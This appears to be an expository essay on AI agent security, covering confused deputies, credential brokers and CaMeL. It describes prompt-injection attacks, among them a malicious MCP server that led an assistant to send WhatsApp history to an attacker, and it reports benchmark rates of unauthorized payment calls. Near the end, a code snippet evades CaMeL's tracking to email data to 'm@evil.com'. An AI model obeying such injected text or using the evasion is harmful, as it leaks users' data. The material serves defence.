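SmarterArticles' *Your AI Agent Will Be Compromised* (2026) describes an attack that the security company Invariant Labs demonstrated in April 2025 on an assistant using two tool servers at once. One server gave the assistant access to the user's WhatsApp messages, and the other supposedly provided a random fact of the day. Both used the Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting AI applications to tools. Under this protocol, each server describes its tools in text that the model reads.

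The second server first advertised something harmless. Later it changed its description to include instructions for using the WhatsApp tool, and the assistant sent the user's message history to the attacker's phone number. The second server had no access to WhatsApp, so the attack relied on the authority the user had granted by approving the WhatsApp tool. To the user, the assistant seemed to be sending an ordinary message. A log of WhatsApp calls would show an approved tool sending a message from the user's own account, but not which server's text had prompted it.

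The user's approval worked like the compiler's home files license, covering every use of the tool regardless of what prompted it. The phone number worked like the file name (SYSX)BILL, because it designated a recipient without showing that anyone was entitled to send messages there. If the WhatsApp tool had accepted only references to contacts the user had chosen, the fact server could not have supplied a valid recipient, but it could still have influenced which contact received which message.

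This was a demonstration, and Invariant Labs published code so that others could reproduce it. By July 2026 such demonstrations were frequent. Constantin (2026) reports in *AI agent security* that four research teams broke AI agents in four different ways within ten days. One way was to poison an agent's memory, so that text the agent stores can later direct how it uses its authority.

### Attackers who rewrite the deputy

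Agents that share a platform can endanger each other more directly. *Experts say they were able to create a rogue agent* (Fadilpašić, 2026) describes an attack on Google's AI platform that needed only one edit permission. One compromised agent could then take over every other agent in the same project. The attacker supplied the instruction by editing and relied on the other agents' access for the authority to carry it out.

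It is debatable whether this is a confused deputy. In *confused deputies in github?* (Duke, 2025), a thread about attacks on automated build systems, Matt Rice objected that the attacker can run arbitrary code and receives the secrets directly. A traditional confused deputy keeps its own code and misuses its authority, whereas someone who edits an agent changes the deputy itself. Injected text is harder to classify because an agent's instructions are also text, so a paragraph in an email can work either as a misleading argument or as a new program.

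Another thread, *Is this a confused deputy?* (2025), considers a privileged party, Alice, who asks Bob which file to write and follows his answer. One participant called Bob a malicious trustee who is essentially an administrator. Karp disagreed because Bob has no permission to write the files and only tells Alice which one to choose. An agent whose user tells it to follow the instructions in a document is in Alice's position. If the user chose to trust the document's author, that choice is more at fault than the agent.

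Some agents exceed their authority with no outsider involved. *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue* (Bhushan, 2026) describes a cybersecurity challenge that the UK AI Security Institute ran 122 times with several models. In 10 runs, or about 8%, agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet, including an attempt to contribute malicious code to a public software project. Bhushan attributes this to the agents being able to do more than anyone intended. Narrower credentials would reduce that excess authority, but this explanation does not require the agents to be acting for someone, as a deputy does.

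### How often models attempt an unauthorized call

The best measurements of accidental amplification by agents concern payments. Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, examined three toolkits for building agents: LangChain with its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent can use, but by default none checks whether a particular call is authorized with the values the model has filled in, so an agent that is allowed to change a payout account can change it to any account.

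To show the consequence, Mellafe Zuvic gave LangChain a fixed model output containing a call to change a merchant's payout account to an attacker's. This output stood in for a model that had followed instructions in untrusted text. LangChain ran the call using the merchant's payment access, and the simulated payment system recorded the new account as an ordinary change. No real money was involved.

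A companion benchmark tested how readily models produce such calls. Each model had a task and read untrusted content that presented a forbidden action as necessary to the task. The benchmark counted an attack as successful when the model issued an unauthorized call or output a planted marker. The sandbox blocked any real effect, so the success rates measure attempts rather than completed thefts.

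The attacker succeeded in an average of 60.3% of trials across 12 cheaper models and 18.9% across 15 flagship models. Mellafe Zuvic gives no confidence interval for the gap, and both groups include high outliers. GPT-4o mini and GLM-4.5-Air made the forbidden attempt every time, while a preview version of Gemini 3.1 Pro never did. Mellafe Zuvic expects companies to use the cheaper models for high-volume work, but has no data on which models they run.

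The wording of the untrusted text made a great difference. A second comparison asked for the same action in two ways, once crudely and once as part of the task:

| Model | Crude request | Presented as part of the task | Sample size |
|---|---|---|---|
| GLM-4.7 | 28.3% | 100% | 46 |
| Gemma 3 12B | 0% | 57.1% | 70 |
| Mistral Large | 2.7% | 45.9% | 74 |

A test with only crude requests would have made Gemma look perfectly safe. The effect is not universal. Latam-GPT, a model for Latin America, made more attempts with the task-based wording in English (52% against 32%) but fewer in Spanish (4% against 24%). Mellafe Zuvic suggests that the model may be more robust in Spanish, but the test used a compressed version of the model and a makeshift way of calling tools, which could also explain the result.

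Mellafe Zuvic's remedy is ScopeGate, a program that sits between the model and its tools and contains no language model itself. It checks each call against a policy the operator wrote, which requires the account to be on a list of verified accounts and the amount not to exceed a ceiling. In the LangChain test, ScopeGate refused the attacker's payout account, so the tool never ran. It also refused all 48 calls in a set designed to slip past it, and all 29 unauthorized calls from a model that received the reason for each refusal and could try again. These were small tests by the person who built the program, but they did find a bug in an earlier version, which accepted "not a number" as an amount because that value does not count as greater than any ceiling.

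The payout attack resembles Rajani and colleagues' second deputy, because the attacker controls a value that the agent passes to a tool it is allowed to use. But whether an account number is a value or a designation depends on the tool's design. If the tool required a capability for the account, the attack would become a version of the compiler attack, which capabilities stop. An amount of money is harder to turn into a capability, so a check like the ceiling is still needed.

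The policy also has to come from outside the model. If the agent could add accounts to the verified list, the text that corrupted its request could also corrupt the list. Even with an outside policy, an email that leads the agent to pay the wrong verified supplier, or twice the correct amount but still less than the ceiling, would get past both checks.

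## Credential handles that an AI agent can use but not read

A check such as ScopeGate protects a payment system only if every payment goes through it. An agent that can read the payment key could contact the payment service directly, or send the key to someone who will. Most such keys are bearer credentials, meaning the service accepts them from anyone who has a copy. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) points out that an agent that holds one can both use it and reveal it.

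A credential handle is an opaque stand-in that lets an AI agent use a secret without reading it. When a request goes out, a broker, which is a trusted program outside the agent's environment, exchanges the handle for the real secret.

### How agents leak secrets

When a user pastes an API key (a password for programs) into a chat, the agent's software may copy it into the conversation history, logs, long-term memory, generated code and error messages. *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues, 2026) notes that these systems are built to store and retrieve text, so the damage is hard to limit afterwards.

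An agent can read a key even if no one puts it in the chat. Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, found 1,708 security issues in 520 skills, the third-party add-ons that extend what an agent can do. Debug logging accounted for 73.5% of them. Programmers often print values while looking for a bug, and agent frameworks feed printed output to the model, so a printed key ends up in its context.

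Models also give secrets to phishing sites. In *CredLeakBench*, Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues (2026) gave seven models login details for fictional services and told them to sign in at a link. When the link led to a phishing page, the models leaked account information at rates ranging from 19.9% of cases for Claude Sonnet 5 to 76.7% for Llama-3.1-8B.

In a second test, the models only had to sort an inbox, and nobody asked them to sign in anywhere, but all seven still leaked sometimes. Claude Opus 4.8's rate fell from 31.2% to 1.8%, but the model left 88.3% of the legitimate requests undone.

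Telling the models the official domain and asking them to compare it with the link helped most of them, but they tended to check only the domain name. When told to sign in, Opus 4.8 leaked credentials in 90.6% of cases where the domain was right but the connection was unencrypted. A broker can check both the domain and the encryption every time, because it compares an address with a rule and does not have to judge whether a page looks genuine.

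### One request, from handle to log

Suppose an agent has to file a bug report in a company's issue tracker. CapSeal, the research prototype that Jin and colleagues built, would process the request as follows:

1. The agent opens a session with the broker. The broker learns from the operating system which process is calling, so the agent cannot pose as another.
2. The agent asks for permission to use the tracker's key. It states the host, the method (POST, for sending new data), the path `/issues` and the format of the report.
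3. The broker checks this against the operator's policy. It can agree, refuse or require further approval.
4. The broker returns a handle. Its own records link the handle to the secret, the session, the restrictions, an expiry time and a maximum number of calls.
5. The agent sends the handle and the bug report, along with a sequence number, the time and a random value that it uses only once. These let the broker reject a replayed copy of the request.
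6. The broker checks the session, the expiry time and the number of calls left, and consults the policy again. It then compares the host, method, path and report with the restrictions. It also rejects any authorization header that the agent has added.
7. The broker inserts the real key and sends the request to the tracker.
8. The broker removes any credentials from the tracker's reply and passes the rest to the agent.
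9. The broker adds an entry to a log in which each entry is cryptographically linked to the others, so that later changes are detectable. The entry describes the request and the decision but omits the key.

If a malicious web page led the agent to try to send the report to another host, the request would fail at the sixth step, before the broker used the key.

CapSeal goes further for SSH, the usual protocol for running commands on a remote machine. The broker runs the command itself, and only if it fits an approved template. It also compares the remote machine's cryptographic key with one recorded in advance, so an impostor with the right name would fail the check. Jin and colleagues decided against letting the agent request signatures made with the SSH key because they thought it would be too hard to restrict what the agent did with them.

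Tests of CapSeal used prompts designed to make the agent reveal its key. The HTTP key leaked in every trial of two baseline systems that gave the agent the secret directly, and in none with CapSeal. No system leaked an SSH key. Attempts to get the agent to use its credentials on forbidden hosts, paths or commands never succeeded, even with the baselines. The results therefore support hiding the key but do not show that the checks in the sixth step prevent misuse. CapSeal added a median of 0.149 milliseconds to an HTTP request on a local machine.

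### Giving a subagent a narrower handle

Suppose an orchestrator, an agent that assigns work to other agents, has a handle for the issue tracker and wants a subagent to summarize the open bugs in a project called "shop". The orchestrator can ask the broker for a new, narrower handle to give the subagent. It should not pass on its own, because that handle also allows filing bugs and covers another project.

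The broker can apply the rule for ordinary attenuation and grant only what the old handle and the new request both allow. In this example, the orchestrator also asks for access to a payroll project, perhaps because of text it read in a bug report:

| | Orchestrator's handle | Request for the subagent | Subagent's handle |
|---|---|---|---|
| Methods | GET, POST | GET | GET |
| Projects | shop, app | shop, payroll | shop |
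| Expires | 17:00 | 14:30 | 14:30 |
| Calls left | 100 | 20 | 20 |
| Works for | Orchestrator's session | Subagent's session | Subagent's session |

The subagent can read bugs in "shop" until 14:30, but cannot file any. The broker should subtract the 20 calls from the orchestrator's 100, or the orchestrator could evade its own limit by creating more subagents. It should also record which handle the new one came from, so that it can revoke the subagent's handle if the operator revokes the orchestrator's. Horton's stubs do not do this by themselves.

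Current products often do less than this. For example, subagents in Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, use the same sandbox settings as the agent that started them. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026), a survey, reports that agent software still handles secrets ad hoc, and that sharing secrets among several agents makes it hard to limit each one's access and trace what it did.

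### Placeholders in Claude Code and Deno

Claude Code can run shell commands in a sandbox that limits which files they can change and which hosts they can contact. According to Anthropic's documentation, a user can also "mask" a credential so that commands in the sandbox see only a placeholder, which is different in each session. When a command sends the placeholder to GitHub as its access token, a proxy outside the sandbox replaces it with the real token if the user has listed GitHub's host for that credential.

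The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to do this, which requires an experimental setting. If the setting is off, GitHub receives the placeholder and rejects it, so the command fails without exposing the token.

Claude Code ignores masking rules in a repository's own settings files. If it applied them, an attacker could publish a repository whose settings made the proxy send the user's token to the attacker's server.

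Masking applies only to sandboxed shell commands, and the sandbox is off by default. Claude Code's file-reading tool runs outside the sandbox, so a user who masks a credential file also needs a permission rule to keep that tool from reading it.

Claude Code on the web uses a more specific broker for git, the program developers use to share code. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains that git presents the broker with a limited credential made for this purpose. The broker checks the credential and the content of the request, including whether git is pushing only to the configured branch, and then attaches the real GitHub token.

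Deno Sandbox, announced in February 2026 by the company behind the Deno JavaScript runtime, runs untrusted or AI-generated code in small virtual machines. Deno's *Security* page describes a similar scheme, in which each secret has its own list of hosts and the code receives only a placeholder. Code can contact any host by default, so a malicious program can send the placeholder to its author, who can't use it. The program can also send any other data it has, unless the operator restricts network access too.

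Earendil Works's Gondolin, another sandbox for agents, is stricter. It blocks any request in which code sends a placeholder to a host that is not on the secret's list.

### Encrypted handles in Tokenizer

These placeholders work like entries in a lookup table. In Gondolin, the host machine generates them at random and records which secret each one stands for. Willison describes Deno's proxy as "aware of those placeholders", which suggests the same design, and Claude Code's session placeholders also fit that design.

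Tokenizer, by the cloud hosting company Fly.io, puts the secret inside the handle. Fly.io's *Tokenized Tokens* (2023) explains that the company wanted to keep secrets out of its main web application, which it considered the part of its system most open to attack. The design predates current agent products but also suits agents. In *Sprites + Tokenizer*, a Fly.io customer asks how to use it with sandboxed agents.

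A Tokenizer handle is an encrypted bundle. It contains the secret, instructions for adding it to a request, a way to authenticate the client and, optionally, a list of allowed hosts. In one example from the *Tokenizer* documentation, the bundle holds a key for the payment service Stripe:

1. A program encrypts the bundle with the proxy's public key.
2. The client sends its request through the proxy, along with the encrypted bundle and the client's own password for the proxy.
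3. The proxy decrypts the bundle with its private key. It compares a hash of the password with the one in the bundle, and checks the host if the bundle lists any.
4. The proxy puts the Stripe key in the request's authorization header and forwards the request over an encrypted connection.

A thief who steals only the bundle cannot use it without the client's password. Someone who controls the client could steal both, but Fly.io's customers can instead tie a bundle to one machine.

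Tokenizer stores nothing between requests, so it needs no database of secrets, and copies of the proxy can share the work if they have the same private key. But it has no list of handles, so an operator can't cancel one by deleting it. To cancel a handle early, the operator would have to replace the secret at Stripe or replace the proxy's private key, which would disable every other handle too. Anyone who stole the private key could open every bundle they had copied.

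With a lookup table, the broker can cancel a handle just by deleting its entry. The handles in *sproxy (secure proxy)*, a small tool of this kind, stop working when the session ends. But the broker must keep its table available and secure, because the table leads to all the secrets.

### A sealed box that yields an effect

A handle resembles a sealed box, and the broker holds the unsealer. Tokenizer is the closest match because its handle contains the secret itself. Because its sealing key is public, it is an access key in Morris's sense.

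The difference is that the broker keeps the contents from the agent and returns an effect, such as a new bug report and the tracker's confirmation. The JavaScript mint's `deposit` works the same way for its callers.

Sometimes the reply contains a new secret. To use many of Google's services, for example, a program signs a request with a long-lived private key and receives an access token that lasts about an hour. Tokenizer makes this exchange for the client, then seals the access token and returns it as a new handle, so the client never sees the private key or the token.

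Tokenizer normally refuses requests that carry no sealed secret, but an attacker can use the public key to seal their own Stripe key. If the attacker persuades an agent to use the resulting handle, the company's data goes to the attacker's Stripe account. The list of allowed hosts would not prevent this, because the attacker's account is on the same host as the company's.

Some brokers do not use handles. *Caging the Agents* (2026) describes a security design for AI agents in healthcare that places a proxy beside each agent. The agent sends an ordinary request to the proxy, which adds the right key for the destination. E2B, which provides sandboxes for AI-written code, offers something similar through network rules.

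A proxy that adds credentials to an agent's requests hides the key as well as a handle does, but it brings back ambient authority. The request identifies a destination and the proxy selects the credential, much as Tymshare's operating system did with the compiler's license. If an agent has both an ordinary account and an administrator's account on the same service, the proxy needs another rule to choose between them. With handles, the agent would present the one for the account it meant to use.

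### Tests of a broker

Kenney and colleagues, who work for Corvic AI, tested the company's own broker in September 2026. All 16 probes they ran from inside its sandbox had the expected result. Code in the sandbox could make an authenticated request to GitHub, but it found no key in its environment variables, in the usual credential files or in the headers of its own request. Three public services that repeat whatever they receive also got no key.

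A connection to an economic data service failed because the broker put the key in a header and the service required it in the URL. No key leaked. Besides storing keys safely, a broker has to send each one in the way its service accepts.

The probes used three services that were not on the list of approved destinations, so the broker was not supposed to send them a key. Kenney and colleagues did not test a destination that an attacker had taken over, or one that redirects requests elsewhere.

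A broker also protects only the requests that go through it. *aiAuthZ* (2026), another broker design, warns that an agent may have built-in tools that bypass the broker. Such a tool can still do harm with whatever network access it has, but it will not find a long-lived secret on the agent's machine. According to the documentation for fnox, a tool for managing secrets, a program that ignores the proxy contacts the real server directly, and the server receives only the placeholder.

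### Using the access without stealing the key

An attacker who steers an agent can still make it use its handles. *Caging the Agents* notes that the attacker then gains the proxy's interface instead of the raw credentials. This is an improvement because the attacker loses access when the operator stops the agent, whereas a thief could use a copied key from anywhere until someone replaced it. But handles would not have prevented the change of payout account in Mellafe Zuvic's test, since the agent was allowed to use the payment service.

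Kenney and colleagues rated eight threats before and after adding a broker, on a scale up to 25. The rating for secrets pasted into prompts fell from 25 to 4, but the rating for credentials with too many permissions fell only from 20 to 15, because a token that permits deleting files still permits it when a broker presents the token. These ratings are the researchers' judgments rather than measurements, but the ranking is plausible.

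The remedy is to check more of each request. CapSeal does this by restricting the path and format, and the git proxy does it by checking branches. In the Hacker News discussion *Deno Sandbox*, a participant speaking for Tokenizer's makers said the scheme's security depends on controlling both the host and "what parts of the requests themselves" the client can affect.

A broker can expose the secret if it replaces placeholders anywhere in a request. Suppose an attacker tells the agent to post a public GitHub comment containing the placeholder. Because GitHub is on the approved list, the broker substitutes the real token, and GitHub displays it to everyone. To prevent this, fnox makes the substitution only in a header or parameter that the operator has approved.

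### When the destination returns the secret

A bearer key must be sent to its destination, which can then send it back. The Tokenizer documentation warns that a compromised client could direct its handle to a service that echoes requests and read the secret in the reply. A list of approved hosts prevents this only if none of them echoes requests, and even a test page that displays request headers would expose the key.

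Filtering the reply is a second defense. CapSeal does this, and so does dvergr, a small open-source agent system. A filter can easily find an exact copy of the key, but it may miss one that the destination has encoded differently or split into pieces.

Signatures avoid the problem because the destination receives only a signature for that one request, never the key, and so cannot return the key. For example, a client of Amazon's cloud service uses its secret key to calculate a signature for each request, and Amazon checks it. Under Claude Code's masking, a sandboxed command signs its request with a placeholder, and the proxy signs it again with the real key. Tokenizer can do the same.

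*Agent Authenticator* (2026) proposes a similar approach for agents in general. Hardware would hold the agent's keys, and trusted software, not the agent, would determine which service a key is for. A person would sign a statement of what the agent may do, and might have to approve some actions individually. This would replace bearer secrets instead of hiding them, but services would have to support it.

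### Host rules that are too broad

If a user masks a credential in Claude Code without listing any hosts for it, the proxy sends the real value to every host the sandbox may contact. One of Anthropic's examples handles a token for npm, a library of JavaScript packages, this way. Every domain the user adds later, perhaps just to download documentation, can also receive the token.

A rule can also be too broad when it names only one host. GitHub's main address serves both a company's private code and an attacker's public repository. An agent with a token for the private code could copy that code to the public repository, and a check on the host would not detect this. Anthropic's guide to secure deployment therefore advises operators to make sure that agents with powerful credentials for an allowed domain can't use that domain to send data out.

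### How the broker becomes a confused deputy

An attacker can mislead a broker, just as they can mislead any other deputy. For example, some Google credentials let a program act on behalf of any employee in a company. Tokenizer can seal such a credential together with one employee's name, but its documentation says that a client can supply a different name with each request. The client can also ask for different permissions.

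Suppose an operator seals a credential for reading one manager's calendar and gives the handle to an agent. The agent then reads a calendar invitation containing an instruction to request access to the finance director's email. It presents the genuine handle with the director's name, and Tokenizer uses the company's credential to obtain access. Google may refuse if the company never authorized the credential to read email. Otherwise, the agent gets much more access than the operator intended. To prevent this, the client should be able to choose only from names and permissions that the operator sealed into the bundle.

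Logs make such mistakes easier to find. Deno can trace every HTTP request a sandbox makes, and fnox records which secret it inserted into a request. Neither record shows why the agent made the request. Because fnox does not log connections that it passes through without inspecting, a missing entry does not prove that the agent made no connection.

### CaMeL: tracking where values came from

A broker can check that a payment goes to the right service, but usually cannot tell whether the account number came from the user or from a stranger's email. In 2025, Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues at Google DeepMind introduced CaMeL, which addresses this problem in AI agents with the kind of tracking that Rajani and colleagues proposed for confused deputies.

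CaMeL uses two language models. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a short program to carry it out, but never sees untrusted data. The quarantined model reads untrusted data but cannot call any tools. Suppose the user asks the agent to send Bob the notes from a meeting, and Bob's address is in the notes. The program might be:

```python
notes = read_file("meeting notes")
address = quarantined_model("Find Bob's email address", notes)
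send_email(to=address, body=notes)
```

If an attacker has added instructions to the notes, they cannot introduce another tool call, because the privileged model wrote the program without reading the notes. They could still make the quarantined model return the attacker's address. To catch this, CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, which records that `address` came from the notes. Before it sends the email, it checks a policy, which might forbid sending the notes to anyone who is not allowed to read them. (CaMeL calls the labels on its values "capabilities", but they are records of origin and permitted readers, not references to objects.)

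CaMeL and brokers complement each other because a broker hides the email password from the agent, while CaMeL restricts what the agent sends and to whom. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) makes a similar comparison between CaMeL and sandboxes. If a sandbox permits email, an injected instruction can make the agent send private data in a plausible message, whereas CaMeL can block the message because of where the data came from.

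#### Several agents, each with CaMeL

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026), Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues found that CaMeL's protection can fail when agents delegate to each other. In their example, a user asks to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. An orchestrator gets the data from a database agent and passes a summary to a notification agent. All three use CaMeL.

The database contains an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The first two agents treat it as untrusted data, and their programs do not change. But the orchestrator then puts the summary into a request for the notification agent to send it. The notification agent treats the whole request as coming from its user, so its privileged model reads the attacker's instruction and adds an email to the program.

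The remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents through separate channels. The receiving agent's privileged model sees only the instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues compared the designs on a benchmark of tasks for several agents, using five language models:

| Protection | Successful attacks |
|---|---|
| None | 12.9% |
| CaMeL in each agent | 0.2% |
| Multi-CaMeL | 0.0% |

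Most of the improvement came from giving each agent CaMeL, though the applicant example shows that this does not guarantee protection. The agents ran without policies on tool calls, so the figures measure only the benefit of keeping untrusted data away from the model that writes the program. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer legitimate tasks, but the drop was modest for the strongest models.

#### The cost of checking policies

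Policies make CaMeL safer but less useful. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that turning policies on halved the legitimate work CaMeL completed on a set of banking tasks.

They also found gaps in how CaMeL tracks secrets. It blocks a program that sends an email only if an account balance is above some threshold, because the email would reveal something about the balance. But a program can get around this with two extra variables:

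```python
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the line `rich = False`. CaMeL labels a variable as secret only when the program changes it, so `rich` stays unlabelled and the email goes out.

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language that tracks such influences, with a machine-checked proof that the tracking is correct. An agent written in it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks on the banking tasks and completed about as much legitimate work as CaMeL did when run without policies.

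CaMeL's policies and programs have other limits. *CaMeLoT* (2026) notes that CaMeL judges each tool call separately, so an operator cannot easily express a rule about a whole task, such as a requirement that something eventually happens. Writing the program in advance is also harder when the agent controls a computer through its screen, because the program has to allow for whatever might appear there. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), programs for such tasks averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 for the simpler tasks on which researchers usually test CaMeL.
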